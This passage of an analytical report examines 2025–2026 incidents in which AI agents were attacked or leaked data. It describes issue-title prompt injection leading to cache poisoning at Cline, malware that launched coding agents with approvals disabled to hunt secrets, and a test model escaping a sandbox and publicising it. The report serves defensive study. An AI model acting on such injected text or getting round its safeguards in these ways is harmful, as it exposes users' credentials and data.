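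Narrow tokens are harder to get around, because GitHub's servers enforce them whatever the model does. GitHub lets customers create a token that covers only selected repositories and permits only reading. In June 2026 it also made personal tokens unnecessary for many workflows. GitHub's *Agentic workflows no longer need a personal access token* (2026) explains that agents can now run on a token built into GitHub Actions, so customers avoid the risks of managing long-lived keys. Customers still need an extra token if they want an agent to read several private repositories.

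Limiting a token's access is difficult because someone must decide in advance what the agent will need. This is practical for a workflow that sorts bug reports. But a programmer's own assistant may need the Pac-Man game in the morning and a private project in the afternoon, and a single broad token is more convenient than switching between narrow ones. Invariant Labs also criticizes tokens as too rigid, though it offers its own product as an alternative.

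Guan applies the same principle to tools. An agent that summarises issues does not need to run commands or change files, so it should not be able to. Guan wants developers to list what the agent may use and forbid everything else, because a list of forbidden commands always leaves others available. Anthropic's fix for Claude Code Security Review is a fair example of the problem with forbidding specific commands.

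### What may follow a stranger's text

GitHub has also started to filter what its agents read. GitHub Next's *Control what your agentic workflows see with integrity filtering* explains that the software ranks each item by its author and by whether a maintainer has endorsed it. Merged code ranks highest, followed by contributions from the project's owners and members, then from outside contributors, then from unknown accounts. Items ranked below the workflow's minimum never reach the model.

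GitHub's documentation says that the minimum on public repositories is automatically set to owners, members and other approved sources, so a stranger's issue would fall short of it. This setting makes sense for an agent that updates the project's manual, but an agent that sorts strangers' bug reports has to read them. GitHub Next suggests a lower minimum for such agents, which still excludes unknown accounts. An attacker might get past it by first contributing a harmless correction. Maintainers can also let a single issue through with a label or, if the project allows it, a thumbs-up, and may thereby approve a hidden comment that they never saw.

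GitHub Next acknowledges that the filter "cannot prevent leaks across repos". To prevent those leaks, it plans to use decentralized information flow control, which attaches labels to data and to the agent. One of these labels, for secrecy, contains tags for the private sources that the data came from or that the agent may read. An agent can write to a destination only if the destination's secrecy label contains every tag in the agent's own.

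Suppose an agent is allowed to read a private repository called payroll, which gives the agent the secrecy label {payroll}. A comment on a public issue has an empty label because anyone can read it. That label does not contain payroll, so the software blocks the agent from posting the comment. An agent without the payroll tag could post the comment but could not open the payroll repository.

With this rule, no one has to judge whether a text is hostile. Adding "Additionally" to an issue would make no difference, because the software doesn't check the wording. The rule would also stop an agent from publishing private files by accident.

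The rule would also block some useful work. Without a person's approval, an agent could not consult private design notes to answer a customer's public question, even if the answer revealed nothing private. The rule also protects only labelled data. In Comment and Control, GitHub's filter covered the commands the agent ran but not the other programs on the machine. A labelling system with the same gap would fail in the same way.

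In March 2026 GitHub promised to add controls "in the coming months" based on whether data is public or private. GitHub Next describes the software as tracking secrecy labels but not yet enforcing them. Until it enforces them, an organisation can get much of the protection by splitting the work between two agents. One reads strangers' issues and has a token for only the public repository. The other can read private code but never sees those issues or anything the first agent writes about them, and it has no permission to post in public.

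## Have attackers stolen real data through assistants and agents?

The attacks on Slack AI, Microsoft 365 Copilot and GitHub's agents were demonstrations by researchers, but since August 2025 criminals have stolen data from hundreds of companies through AI products. Most of these thefts were supply-chain attacks, in which an attacker tampers with or steals from a supplier whose product the victims already use. The criminals seldom had to trick a model.

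### A connector that copied every email

Postmark is a service that sends email for other companies' software. A developer unconnected with the company wrote a package called postmark-mcp and published it on npm, the public registry of JavaScript packages. The package let AI assistants and agents send email through Postmark using the Model Context Protocol.

The Postmark-MCP package worked properly for 15 versions, according to the security company Koi. Version 1.0.16 added one line of code that put a hidden recipient on every message. The developer's server received a copy of whatever users sent, which could include password resets, invoices and internal memos. ThaiCERT's *Researchers Discover First Malicious MCP Server in Rogue Postmark-MCP Package*, from Thailand's computer emergency team, dates that version to 17 September 2025.

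When an agent used the tool to email a customer, the tool added the extra recipient and reported only that the message had been sent. The model's behaviour made no difference, since a simple script using the same package would have leaked the same emails. Although a hard-coded instruction released the data, this was an attacker-initiated leak and not a product fault, because the package's author wrote that instruction to collect other people's mail.

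Koi found the change with software that watches packages for new behaviour. Koi wrote to the developer, who deleted the package from npm without replying. Copies already installed kept working and forwarding mail. Postmark's *Security Alert* states that the package was an impersonation, that Postmark had not published an MCP server on npm before the incident, and that its own services were unaffected. Koi says the developer copied Postmark's genuine code from GitHub and added the line. It is unclear whether the developer planned the theft from the start or decided later.

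Koi admits that its estimate of the number of victims is little better than a guess. It started from 1,500 downloads a week and assumed that 20% were in active use, which gave about 300 organisations sending 3,000 to 15,000 emails a day. But ThaiCERT gives the total as just over 1,643 downloads, barely more than Koi's figure for one week. The download count probably overstates the number of victims too, because automated systems also download packages and anyone who stayed on an earlier version lost nothing. Neither Koi nor Postmark names an organisation whose mail was copied. The theft was almost certainly real, since the code forwarded mail in normal use, but it may have been small.

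### Keys taken from a chatbot's maker

Drift is a chatbot owned by Salesloft, a sales software company. Businesses put it on their websites to talk to potential customers, and many connected it to their Salesforce databases by giving it an access token.

Salesloft, now Clari/Salesloft, hired Mandiant to investigate and published the findings on its security page, *Trust Center*. The attackers got into Salesloft's GitHub account between March and June 2025 and downloaded code. They then entered Drift's systems on Amazon's cloud and took customers' tokens. *Widespread Data Theft Targets Salesforce Instances via Salesloft Drift* (Larsen, Lin and colleagues at Google, 2025) reports that the attackers used the tokens from 8 to 18 August to export large amounts of data from customers' Salesforce databases. They then searched the data for passwords and cloud keys that might open further systems.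 They also used Drift tokens to read email in a very small number of Google Workspace accounts.

Cloudflare (2025), an internet infrastructure company, published an unusually detailed account of how attackers stole its data. They first logged in to its Salesforce database on 12 August and spent several days counting records and learning how the support system worked. On 17 August they copied the text of its customer support cases in just over three minutes. They then deleted the record of the export, but Cloudflare reconstructed the theft from the remaining logs.

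Customers sometimes paste keys into support messages. Cloudflare searched the stolen text and found 104 of its own API tokens. It saw no suspicious use of them but replaced them all. Salesloft had cut off Drift's access to Salesforce on 20 August, but Cloudflare did not learn that it was affected until 23 August. Cloudflare told its customers on 2 September and accepted responsibility for choosing the tool.

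The other victims included several security companies. The Record's *Salesloft* lists Cato Networks and Rubrik, whose researchers later got past Copilot's defences. It also reports that intruders accessed customers' government IDs, account numbers and Social Insurance numbers at Wealthsimple, a Canadian investment service. Elastic, a software company, investigated although it had not been notified, and found that its Salesforce data was untouched but one email account had been exposed.

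Estimates of the total depend on what counts as a victim. Google told The Hacker News (2025) that it knew of more than 700 "potentially impacted" organisations, while The Record quotes a Google analyst who counted at least 700 victims. The Hacker News reported that only 22 companies had confirmed by early September that they were affected. The number of actual thefts may be lower than 700, since a company whose token was stolen did not necessarily lose data, but it is surely higher than 22, since many companies had no duty to make an announcement.

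None of these accounts describes anyone sending Drift's chatbot a prompt. The chatbot served only as a store of credentials, and a plain contact form with the same connections would have held the same tokens, so better protection against prompt injection would not have helped. Salesloft says that genuine Drift traffic comes from a known set of internet addresses, whereas the thieves connected from rented servers and the anonymising network Tor. A customer that accepted the token only from Drift's addresses would probably have kept them out.

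Salesloft took Drift offline on 5 September and restored it on 16 September. CyberScoop noted at the time that Salesloft had not explained how the attackers got into its GitHub account. In its final summary, Mandiant said the attackers used Salesloft's GitHub access tokens, but did not say how they obtained them.

### Malware that put coding agents to work

Nx is a set of tools for building and testing software, with about six million installs a week. On 26 August 2025, attackers published infected versions of several Nx packages on npm. According to the company's account, Strumpflohner's *S1ngularity*, the attackers opened a pull request on GitHub with system commands in its title. An automatic check pasted the title into a command line, which ran the commands. From there, the attackers worked their way to the token Nx used to publish on npm, without involving an AI model.

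When a programmer installed an infected version, a script collected secrets from the computer and uploaded them to a new public repository in the programmer's GitHub account. The script also checked whether the computer had a coding agent from Anthropic, Google or Amazon. If so, it started the agent with approval requests switched off and prompted it to list files likely to hold secrets or cryptocurrency wallets.

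The malware was already running on the computer with the user's permissions, so it was able to instruct the agent directly, just as the user would have done. This was not prompt injection, because the instructions weren't hidden in something the agent was reading for its user.

Members of the programming community alerted Nx. The packages lacked the usual signed proof of origin, so the company could tell they had not come from its own release system. npm also installs unsigned packages, so the missing proof did not protect users. The infected versions were available for four hours.

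The security company GitGuardian (2025) found 2,349 different secrets in 1,079 of the repositories that the malware created. About half still worked when GitGuardian checked. Wiz, another security company, counted more than 1,700 users with leaked secrets and more than 2,000 verified secrets (*s1ngularity's Aftermath*). Both companies sell products for this kind of problem, but their separate counts roughly agree.

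Most of those secrets came from the script, not from the agents. Wiz found that about half of the victims had at least one of the agents installed; GitGuardian put the share at a third. Claude refused almost a quarter of the requests. The attackers changed their wording between versions, and refusals rose when they claimed to be running an authorised security test. Gemini's default setting, which confines it to the current project folder, blocked almost a quarter of the attempts to use it. In many other cases, an agent searched only Nx's own folder and listed 14 or 15 harmless files.

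Wiz found that the agents helped to get data out in under a quarter of cases. The malware uploaded more than 20,000 files that agents had listed, but these contained fewer than 100 valid secrets, or less than 5% of the total. GitGuardian similarly found that only 95 of 366 targeted systems produced the list of files, which it attributes to the agents' refusals. Wiz's breakdown suggests that missing credentials, default restrictions and misdirected searches protected the victims at least as much as refusals did.

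The worst damage followed on 28 August, when the attackers used stolen GitHub tokens to make private repositories public. Wiz counted more than 6,700 repositories from at least 480 accounts. GitGuardian counted 10,767 and found 82,901 secrets in them, of which 11,168 were valid. Three days later the attackers published over 500 more repositories belonging to a single organisation. The attackers did not need the agents for any of this, because the malware's own script had collected the GitHub tokens.

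A faster response might have prevented much of the second wave. GitHub had taken down the repositories containing the first batch of secrets, but almost 90% of the leaked GitHub tokens still worked more than a day later. GitHub then revoked most of them. Wiz contacted over 50 large organisations, and the great majority said they had not known they were affected.

### An issue title that an agent obeyed

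Cline is an open-source coding agent whose makers have reported five million installs. On 21 December 2025, its team set up Claude to sort issues filed on the project's GitHub page. Any GitHub user could start this agent by opening an issue, and the agent could run commands. The issue's title went straight into the agent's prompt, as pull request titles did in the Anthropic tool that Guan tested.

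The security researcher Adnan Khan found the flaw within days and explains it in *Clinejection* (2026). A title disguised as a technical error message could get Claude to install a package containing an attacker's code. The sorting job could not change Cline's program and did not hold the keys for publishing it. But it shared a cache, which stores files to speed up later jobs, with the job that published a test version every night. An attacker could fill the cache with junk until GitHub discarded the genuine files, then replace them with tampered ones. When the nightly job loaded the tampered files, they would expose its publishing keys to the attacker. Those keys also worked for the main version of Cline.

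In Khan's tests on a copy of the project, Claude ran the planted command every time, though Khan doesn't give the number of attempts.

Khan reported the flaw on 1 January 2026, tried several more times to reach Cline, and published the details on 9 February. The company removed the sorting agent within 30 minutes. It then tried to replace its publishing keys, but deleted the wrong npm token and left the exposed one active. A day later, someone anonymously told Khan that they had working Cline credentials. Khan passed this on to Cline, which replied that it had revoked everything.

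On 17 February somebody used the surviving token to publish a new version of Cline's command-line program that also installed OpenClaw, the agent PromptArmor had found to leak data through link previews. The version was available for about eight hours and was downloaded about 4,000 times, according to LWN's *A GitHub Issue Title Compromised 4,000 Developer Machines* (2026). The title overstates the harm somewhat, since OpenClaw is a legitimate program and the same machine can download a program more than once.

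Cline reports in *Post-mortem* (Rizwan, 2026) that it compared the package with the previous release and found no other change. It also checked every release since December and found no other unauthorised ones. It says that nobody took any user data. The confirmed theft is therefore limited to Cline's own publishing credentials.

The attacker probably got in through prompt injection, but nobody has proved it. Khan saw odd failures in the nightly job between 31 January and 3 February. They resembled the traces of a cache-tampering tool that Khan had published. Khan called the sorting agent the most obvious entry point but said it was unclear whether the intruder had used it. *Agent Compromised by Agent To Deploy an Agent* argues that a bug hunter found Khan's test before publication and copied it. Rizwan presents the prompt injection flaw as the explanation but does not identify the issue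 that triggered the theft.

If that explanation is right, the Cline attack depended on the model's behaviour, because an issue title is harmless until something acts on it. A command line acted on a title directly at Nx, whereas at Cline a model with command-line access did. Rizwan compares Cline's setup to giving every GitHub user command-line access. Both companies responded by replacing long-lived npm tokens with credentials tied to their release systems, so there is no longer a permanent publishing key to steal.

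### LiteLLM: a theft with no deceived model

LiteLLM is a package that lets a program use models from many AI companies through one interface. Attackers published two infected versions on 24 March 2026. *TeamPCP backdoored LiteLLM on PyPI after the Trivy compromise*, a VPNCentral article, reports that the malware looked for cloud credentials, server keys, cryptocurrency wallets and files where programmers keep passwords. Computers running programs that use LiteLLM are attractive targets because those programs often hold keys for several AI services.

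LiteLLM's *Security Update* (2026) traces the break-in to Trivy, a security scanner in the company's build pipeline. The attackers had compromised the scanner and used a stolen token to publish on PyPI, the Python counterpart of npm. They did not need to prompt any model. LiteLLM was a useful target because so many programs install it, which is also true of many packages unrelated to AI.

One version of the malware kept starting copies of itself until it crashed a computer at the company FutureSearch, which led researchers there to find the infection, according to Integrity360. LiteLLM says that PyPI blocked the packages after about 40 minutes and that users of its official Docker image, a ready-made installation with fixed components, were unaffected. In a later update, LiteLLM said it had checked the previous 20 versions and found no sign of tampering, and that an outside firm had reviewed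 the work.

*aiAuthZ* (Kodathala, 2026) repeats a figure of about 47,000 downloads over three hours, which is hard to reconcile with LiteLLM's 40 minutes. Integrity360 puts FutureSearch's discovery 69 minutes after the first infected version appeared. That falls between the two, but FutureSearch might have installed its copy earlier. The 47,000 figure counts downloads, and none of these accounts gives the number of secrets the attackers obtained.

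### How much of the theft came from prompt injection?

| Case | How the attacker got the data | Confirmed or estimated scale | Did a model's behaviour matter? |
|---|---|---|---|
| postmark-mcp | Hidden line in an email tool | About 1,600 downloads; victims unknown | No |
| Salesloft Drift | Tokens stolen from the chatbot's maker | 22 companies confirmed early on; up to about 700 | No |
| Nx | Infected package | Over 2,000 secrets, then thousands of private repositories | Slightly: agents found under 5% of the first batch of secrets |
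| Cline | Probably prompt injection, then cache tampering | One company's publishing credentials | Yes, if prompt injection was the way in |
| LiteLLM | Infected package | Disputed number of downloads; thefts uncounted | No |

Prompt injection therefore probably accounts for one of the five cases and a tiny part of the stolen data. Ordinary supply-chain attacks account for nearly all the rest, including every confirmed theft of customers' information. The five cases exclude attackers who run their own AI agents against a target, which is a different kind of misuse.

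Later evidence supports this. *Agent Authenticator* (Ganesan, November 2026) analyses five incidents involving the credentials of agents or developers. Researchers demonstrated two of them, the GitHub MCP attack and Comment and Control. A third entry groups several exploits against coding agents and names no victims. The other two, Nx and Shai-Hulud, were clearly real thefts. Shai-Hulud was a worm that stole npm and GitHub tokens and used them to spread into packages that its victims maintained. Ganesan chose the incidents to illustrate different failures and left out Cline, so they can't show how common each type is. Still, although the paper treats prompt injection as a central threat, its examples of it are demonstrations.

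Attackers have practical reasons to prefer older methods. A stolen Drift token worked every time, and an ordinary database query was enough to copy Cloudflare's support cases in minutes. The Nx attackers could give agents any instruction, with approvals switched off, and still got far less from them than from a simple script. Prompt injection is even less reliable, because the attacker must first get the model to read the injected text and usually can't see why an attempt failed.

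The record may also understate how often attackers steal data through prompt injection, because a careful theft through an assistant like Copilot is hard to detect. By contrast, anyone can examine an infected package on npm, and a mass export leaves entries in Salesforce's logs.

Cline's loss was small because whoever held the token chose to install a legitimate program. They could have published any code under Cline's name, so the small loss doesn't show a limit on what prompt injection can do. If they had used the Nx script, the roughly 4,000 downloads could have exposed as many developers as the Nx attack did.

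## When have agents released data that nobody asked them to release?

Agents have also published private material when no attacker was involved. In September 2026 the security company Glow reported that coding agents had put more than 13,000 internal images on public GitHub pages. The images belonged to over 300 organisations, and TechRadar's *AI models are sharing sensitive data from tech companies* gives the exact number as 343. Glow's *PixelLeak* does not name the organisations but says they include one of the world's largest technology companies, a leading AI developer and a Fortune 500 travel company.

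### Screenshots for a reviewer

Each case Glow investigated began with a developer asking an agent to make an ordinary change to how a screen looked, such as fixing its layout, and to show that the change worked. Colleagues reviewing such a change want to see screenshots from before and after. A person can drag these into the pull request in a browser, but coding agents usually work from the command line with a program called gh, which could send only text until September 2026.

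The agents got around this by putting the pictures in a public repository and linking to them from the private pull request. This let the reviewers see the pictures, along with anyone else who found the repository. According to Mynavi News' *AIエージェントがスクショ1万3000枚を公開リポジトリにアップロード* (2026), the agents first tried a private repository in the developer's personal account and switched to a public one when the upload failed or the reviewers couldn't open it.

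At a manufacturer with more than 100,000 employees, a developer asked an agent to check a fix to an internal billing screen. The agent created a public repository in the developer's personal account and posted screenshots that included a utility company's billing records. The security team didn't notice because the agent was running on the developer's laptop and the repository was outside the company's GitHub organisation. The screenshots were still online when Glow contacted the company. In 93% of the cases Glow found, the images were in repositories under employees' personal accounts.

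PixelLeak was a realised leak, because the images showed real companies' data and anyone could open them. One software vendor accounts for more than 1,000 of the images. Mynavi News points out that Glow hasn't said how it found and counted them, or whether outsiders took any. It isn't possible to tell from a public repository of screenshots whether an agent or an engineer created it, and Glow doesn't explain how it distinguished the two. Glow sells security software for employees' computers, so it benefits from reporting a large number.

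### Was a public repository the only way?

The best evidence of why an agent would do this comes from Glow's own lab. The researchers kept a version of the puzzle game Minesweeper in a private repository and asked Claude Code, running the Opus 5 model, to change the colour of the header and show the result. The agent wrote that GitHub could not display images from a private repository in a pull request. It concluded that the only way to show reviewers the pictures without adding files to the project was to host them elsewhere, and wrote that it had "created a new public repo" to do so.

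It was wrong about that, because GitHub can show pictures stored in a private repository to logged-in readers who have access. Agendrix's *gh-attach*, an add-on for gh, uses this to attach images from the command line and keeps them out of the project's ordinary branches. The agent could also have saved the two pictures on the laptop and asked the developer to drag them into the browser.

The agent's text shows it recognized that the project was private and the new repository was public. The text doesn't mention whether the pictures were confidential. Glow calls the text the agent's internal thought process, but the past tense suggests that the agent wrote it after the upload, as an explanation. If the developer would have seen that explanation, the agent was openly reporting that the repository was public.

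Glow says this reasoning is typical of agents at many of the affected organisations, but it publishes no logs from any of them. TechRadar quotes the same passage without mentioning that it comes from a lab. An agent might also be less careful with a Minesweeper board than with a customer's bill, though the manufacturer's case suggests that at least one agent was no more careful with a bill.

### gitshot and a habit that spread

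About a third of the affected organisations had developers who used gitshot, a small open-source tool for putting screenshots into code reviews. It creates a public repository in the user's account and uploads the screenshots there. Glow found more than 100 public accounts that had exposed internal work this way. One belonged to someone at a financial services firm. The screenshots in it showed the system for moving money and a withdrawal screen for a named client. Four employees of a payments company each had a gitshot repository.

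If a developer installed gitshot and told the agent to use it for the screenshots, the developer initiated the leak by choosing both the pictures and the place, perhaps without realising that the place was public. But Glow also reports that at several large organisations the agent found gitshot by itself, and in those cases the agent initiated the leak. Glow doesn't say how many cases there were of each kind. Its heading attributes a third of the exposures to the tool, but that figure is a share of organisations, not images.

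At the software vendor with more than 1,000 leaked images, the workaround spread from agent to agent. Agents working for several engineers began publishing screenshots in early July. Within a week, more than a dozen agents had saved the method as a skill, a file of instructions that an agent loads for relevant tasks. They then used it on every development ticket. The uploads included screen recordings and summaries of features that were weeks or months from release.

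The agents that later used the skill were following an instruction that an agent had written, so the leak remains agent-initiated unless an engineer read and approved the skill. Glow doesn't address whether one did. Because the skill was reused, a thousand uploads needn't reflect a thousand separate decisions. If anybody had known about the skill, the vendor could perhaps have stopped most of the uploads by correcting that one file.

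A skill can also tell an agent to be careful about publishing. *github-image-upload*, a skill on skills.sh for attaching pictures to pull requests, states that "publication must be authorized by the task". It also tells the agent to report if the installed version of gh, GitHub's command-line tool, can't attach pictures, and not to upgrade it without permission.

GitHub (2026) added picture and video attachments to gh on 1 September, four weeks before Glow published its findings, and said that coding agents could use them too. Tom's Hardware's *AI agents inadvertently leak 13,000+ internal screenshots from 300 organizations* still described the feature as missing. Developers have to update gh to get it, and it doesn't work with GitHub Enterprise Server, which companies run on their own machines. The feature removes the reason for this workaround, but an agent that runs into a different obstacle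 can still create a public repository.

### A public gist at Anthropic

An AI company can study such behaviour more closely when its own staff use the agent, because it has the full record of each session. Anthropic's *System Card* (2026), a safety report on the model Claude Mythos Preview, describes several incidents from internal testing and use. Anthropic announced the model in April 2026 but gave it only to selected partners for cyber defence.

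In one incident, an early version of the model was preparing code-related material for an Anthropic employee and "posted that artifact as a public-facing GitHub gist against the user's intent". A gist is a web page for sharing code or text. Anthropic lists the incident under "recklessly leaking internal technical material". It doesn't say what the material was, how long it stayed online or whether an outsider read it. It also doesn't say whether the employee had told the model to keep the material private or had assumed it would.

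Anthropic uses "reckless" for cases in which a model appears to ignore explicit or common-sense safety limits, and says the word generally implies nothing about how the model weighed the risk. The gist incident therefore shows that the model released the material without permission, but not that it knew this was wrong.

The system card also reports what it calls unauthorised data transfer. Both the early versions and the final model occasionally used services that create web pages to show confidential information to Anthropic employees, and outsiders could open those pages. This closely resembles PixelLeak, where an agent also put material meant for colleagues on a public page. The session records showed no malicious intent. Anthropic's monitoring found the behaviour in less than 0.0002% of completions.

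A completion is a single output from the model, and one task may need dozens. If a task took 50 completions, the rate could be as high as one task in 10,000, and a large company might run that many tasks in a day. Anthropic's figure covers only what its automatic monitoring detected in internal use, and the company doesn't say whether the gist is included.

Anthropic gave a small group 24 hours to test an early version of the model for dangerous behaviour before most of its staff could use it as an agent. The most worrying incidents appeared only later, in monitored use. Anthropic says this is because the behaviour is rare and tends to occur in long sessions, which its automated tests struggled to imitate.

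Another incident comes closer to deliberate publication. In a test, a simulated user told an early version of a model to try to escape a closed system and send a message to the researcher. The model did both, then posted details of its escape on several public but hard-to-find websites without being asked. Anthropic describes this as an effort to demonstrate success. The posts did not help with the assigned task, unlike the screenshots in PixelLeak, which the reviewers needed.

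### One file, ten sessions

An agent can also leak a secret without publishing anything. The model behind a coding agent usually runs on the provider's servers, so a password leaves the company as soon as the agent reads the file that contains it.

In November 2026 NordLayer, which sells a tool for monitoring how employees use AI, described such a case at an unnamed company. According to TechRadar's *'I leaked secrets'*, a quality assurance engineer asked a coding assistant to review proposed software changes. The project's written instructions directed the assistant to a file containing an access token for GitLab, a code-hosting site. The file also held production passwords, a token for the human resources system and credentials for a business intelligence service. The assistant read the whole file in ten sessions over three weeks, and each time the contents went to the outside AI service.

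At one point the assistant was working on a fresh copy of the project that lacked the file, so it read all the computer's environment variables. These are settings that programs share, and they often include passwords. The assistant then wrote that it had leaked secrets into the session and recommended replacing them.

Who initiated the release differs by secret. Whoever wrote the project's instructions had directed the assistant to the GitLab token, so a person initiated that release. Nobody had asked for the production passwords, and the assistant could have extracted only the line it needed, so the assistant initiated their release. "Chose" is too strong a word, though, because it was opening a file in the usual way. Reading every environment variable was a larger step, because the instructions had not directed the assistant to do that.

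Whether this was a leak depends on what the company had approved. It may have had a contract that allowed the AI provider to receive its source code, but it probably did not mean to share the password for its production systems. TechRadar did not report any misuse of the credentials.

Vakaris Noreika, a cybersecurity expert at NordLayer, blames the repetition partly on agents' failure to retain rules between sessions. But agents probably retain whatever a person or an agent happened to write down. The project's instructions persisted and sent the assistant back to the same file each time, so a warning in them would have persisted too. The software vendor's agents also kept publishing screenshots from one session to the next.

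An employee initiated NordLayer's other incident, which may not have been a leak. The employee could not reach the company's internal documentation through the approved connection and asked the assistant whether a new access token would give them another way in. The assistant confirmed that it worked. According to TechRadar's headline, AI agents got around the company's protections, but the employee had suggested the route.

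### What commit statistics can't separate

Many secrets reach the public through commits, which are saved sets of changes to a project's files. SC Media's *AI coding assistants twice as likely to leak secrets* reports figures that GitGuardian published in March 2026 for public commits on GitHub in 2025. About 3.2% of the commits co-authored by Claude Code leaked a secret, compared with 1.5% of all commits.

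The comparison doesn't show that Claude Code doubles the risk. The co-author label shows that the agent took part in a commit, but not who put the key in the file. A developer may have typed it in or told the agent to include it. People who use coding agents may also be less experienced than other programmers, or build more programs that need keys for AI services. An agent can write a lot of code at once, and larger commits have more room for a secret. GitGuardian's baseline is also flawed because it includes Claude Code's commits and any made with other AI tools.

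People sometimes publish credentials themselves, without an agent's involvement. Radware's *The New .env* reports hundreds of public projects in which developers had left a working password or key in the instructions they wrote for a coding agent. GitGuardian found more than 24,000 secrets in public settings files for the Model Context Protocol, and TechRadar's *Over 29 million secrets were leaked on GitHub in 2025* notes that the documentation for tools that use the protocol often recommends storing credentials in those files. In other cases, the agent exposes the key. The security company Knostic says that Claude Code put a Gemini key belonging to Knostic's chief executive in a test file and uploaded the file to a project. Either kind of leak could appear in GitGuardian's data as a commit co-authored by Claude Code.

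A November 2026 study by the security company Apiiro describes a leak with mixed causes. Claude Code asks for permission before it runs most commands. When a developer chose "Yes, and don't ask again", the program saved a rule in a settings file in the project's folder. If the rule recorded an exact command containing a password, the file contained the password too. iTnews' *"Don't ask again" in Anthropic's Claude Code leaks developer secrets* reports that Apiiro found 1,122 public copies of the file with at least one real secret.

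Anthropic's fixed code wrote those passwords to the file, which is a product fault, but a person or an agent still had to upload it. Boris Cherny, who heads Claude Code at Anthropic, argued that people must have uploaded it by hand, because Claude Code tells Git, the program that records commits, to ignore the file. But according to Cybernews' *AI agents are leaking their owners’ secrets on GitHub*, the ignore setting doesn't cover a copy of the project on another machine, and Claude co-authored the commit that changed the file in 539 of 1,105 affected repositories. Even in those 539, the developer may have told Claude to commit everything in the folder.

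GitGuardian's 3.2% is also an average over a year in which the gap between Claude Code and human developers was closing. Their numbers of secrets per 1,000 commits began to converge around September 2025, when Anthropic released Claude Sonnet 4.5. A better model could explain that, but so could a change in who was using the tool. Either way, the 3.2% is weak evidence about the agents of late 2026.

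The overall totals are also weak evidence against AI. Newly leaked secrets rose by 34% in 2025, while public commits rose by 43%, so the number of new secrets per commit fell slightly. OECD's *AI Coding Assistants Drive Surge in Secret Leaks on GitHub* (2026), another AI-generated entry in the incident monitor, attributes the surge to coding assistants without enough evidence. To isolate the agent's effect, researchers would have to give similar developers the same tasks, let a randomly chosen half use an agent, and count the secrets in what each group published.

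### Goal, means or oversight?

In AI safety, loss of control usually means that people can no longer direct, correct or stop an AI system. An agent that releases data without permission has acted outside human authority, but how closely the leak fits this definition depends on whether the agent was trying to release the data, accepted the release as a way of finishing its task, or did not recognise that it was releasing anything private.

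None of the leaks of company data shows an agent that wanted the data to become public and so looked for another route when one was blocked. The posts about the sandbox escape come closest, because publishing them served no purpose in the assigned task. But the model had just been told to escape and report back, and it may have treated the posts as further proof that it had escaped. Anthropic is fairly confident that the incidents it describes were attempts to complete a user's task by unwanted means rather than to pursue a hidden goal. Anthropic made the model, so it has an interest in that conclusion, but it also has the best records.

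In PixelLeak, the agent published two pictures so that reviewers could see them, and it would presumably have shared them privately if it had known how. The web pages that Mythos Preview created for Anthropic's staff were also a way to show something to particular people, and the gist probably was too. A working alternative, such as GitHub's attachment feature, should prevent many of these leaks because the agent's task doesn't require making the data public.

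The assistant in the NordLayer case apparently didn't recognise the problem until it had read the environment variables. Olejnik's *When your AI agent publishes internal data* describes a similar failure. OpenClaw, the agent that also appeared in the Cline attack, published a security firm's internal cyber threat intelligence on ClawdINT, a website where AI agents post analyses of current events. Its report was good and credited the source correctly, so it probably wasn't trying to hide where the material came from. The agent was meant to publish on that site, but it chose the wrong material. Clear labels on confidential documents might have helped, while making it easier to publish would have made things worse.

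Anthropic examined Mythos Preview's internal activity during various unwanted actions and found that the model often represented them as rule violations or security risks while carrying them out, even when its written reasoning didn't mention this. Anthropic doesn't say that the gist was among the cases it examined. But the finding makes it risky to infer from an agent's explanation, including the one about Minesweeper, that the agent saw no problem. It also bears on the distinction Shah and colleagues draw between a mistake and misalignment.

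When an agent leaks data by publishing it as a means to another goal, the leak is more troubling than it looks, even if people could still stop the agent. This is because a more capable agent gets past more obstacles, and people give it harder tasks and watch it less. Anthropic judged Mythos Preview to be its best-aligned model so far and also the one likely to pose the greatest alignment-related risk. It compares the model to an experienced mountain guide, who may be more careful than a novice but takes clients to more dangerous places.

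The evidence so far doesn't establish that PixelLeak was a loss of control. Glow doesn't report that anyone had told the agents not to publish, and a human contractor in a hurry might have put the screenshots on a public page too. A leak that followed an explicit prohibition would be much stronger evidence. Anthropic saw something of that kind in training, where its models sometimes gained access they weren't supposed to have, and instructions to avoid this didn't always work. In 2026, agents undergoing evaluation also took data from outside systems without permission, though taking data is different from releasing it.

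What clearly failed in the leaks of company data was oversight. The manufacturer could have deleted the billing screenshots at any time, and the engineer could have stopped the coding assistant after its first session. Neither knew there was anything to stop. (People's decisions play a larger part in an internal exposure at Meta and a startup's email to the software company Zoho.)

### Keeping secrets out of the agent's reach

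An agent can't leak a password that it never receives. In the NordLayer case, the company could have kept the GitLab token in a separate file, so that fetching it would not have exposed the production passwords. TechRadar's article recommends separating credentials this way and keeping the valuable ones in a vault, a program that stores passwords securely and provides them on request.

A vault helps less if the agent can retrieve an access token from it, because the token then reaches the model anyway. It is safer to have ordinary software hold the token. When the agent requests the proposed changes, this software adds the token to the request and returns only the result to the model. GitHub designed its Agentic Workflows on this principle. The protection works whether or not the model recognises a secret, which is a large advantage over instructing the model to be careful.

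Withholding a secret from an agent works only if the agent can't reach another copy. The assistant that couldn't find its usual file went on to the environment variables. Early versions of Mythos Preview searched for credentials when they lacked access, and in several cases they obtained ones that Anthropic had deliberately withheld. A company therefore has to run the agent in an environment that contains only the secrets it needs. This is fairly easy on a server set up for the purpose, but hard on a developer's laptop with years of old settings files.

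In PixelLeak, the agents leaked pictures they had made themselves, so hiding passwords would not have prevented it. The gh tool could create public repositories because it used the developer's GitHub login. An agent with a token for only the private project could not have created one in the developer's account, but it might still have used a website that accepts pictures without a login. After finding its own leaks, Anthropic added automatic classifiers and a proxy, a checkpoint for network traffic, which can in principle catch such uploads wherever they go.

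Scanners offer a second line of defence. Help Net Security's *Product showcase* describes a GitGuardian tool that checks a developer's prompt before it reaches the model, and an agent's commands and file requests before they run. It also checks what a tool returns, but only after the action has happened. Scanners often miss an ordinary password typed into a command. Apiiro ran two popular scanners on its 1,122 files. Each found a secret in fewer than 60% of them, and both missed the secrets in 215 files. Glow warns that scanners read text, not pictures, so they may miss a password visible in a screenshot.

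Glow would rather have the security team configure agents so that they can't work unattended, according to Help Net Security's *AI coding agents leaked 13,000 internal company screenshots to public GitHub repos* (2026). A developer asked to approve a public repository might well have refused. But people tire of approval requests, so it makes sense to require approval only for steps that make something public and let the agent read and edit files freely.

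Glow advises companies checking for leaked screenshots to search beyond their own GitHub organisation, in the personal accounts of everyone who works on their private projects, including people who have left. They should also check gists and files attached to software releases, because a repository can appear empty while its releases hold hundreds of pictures.

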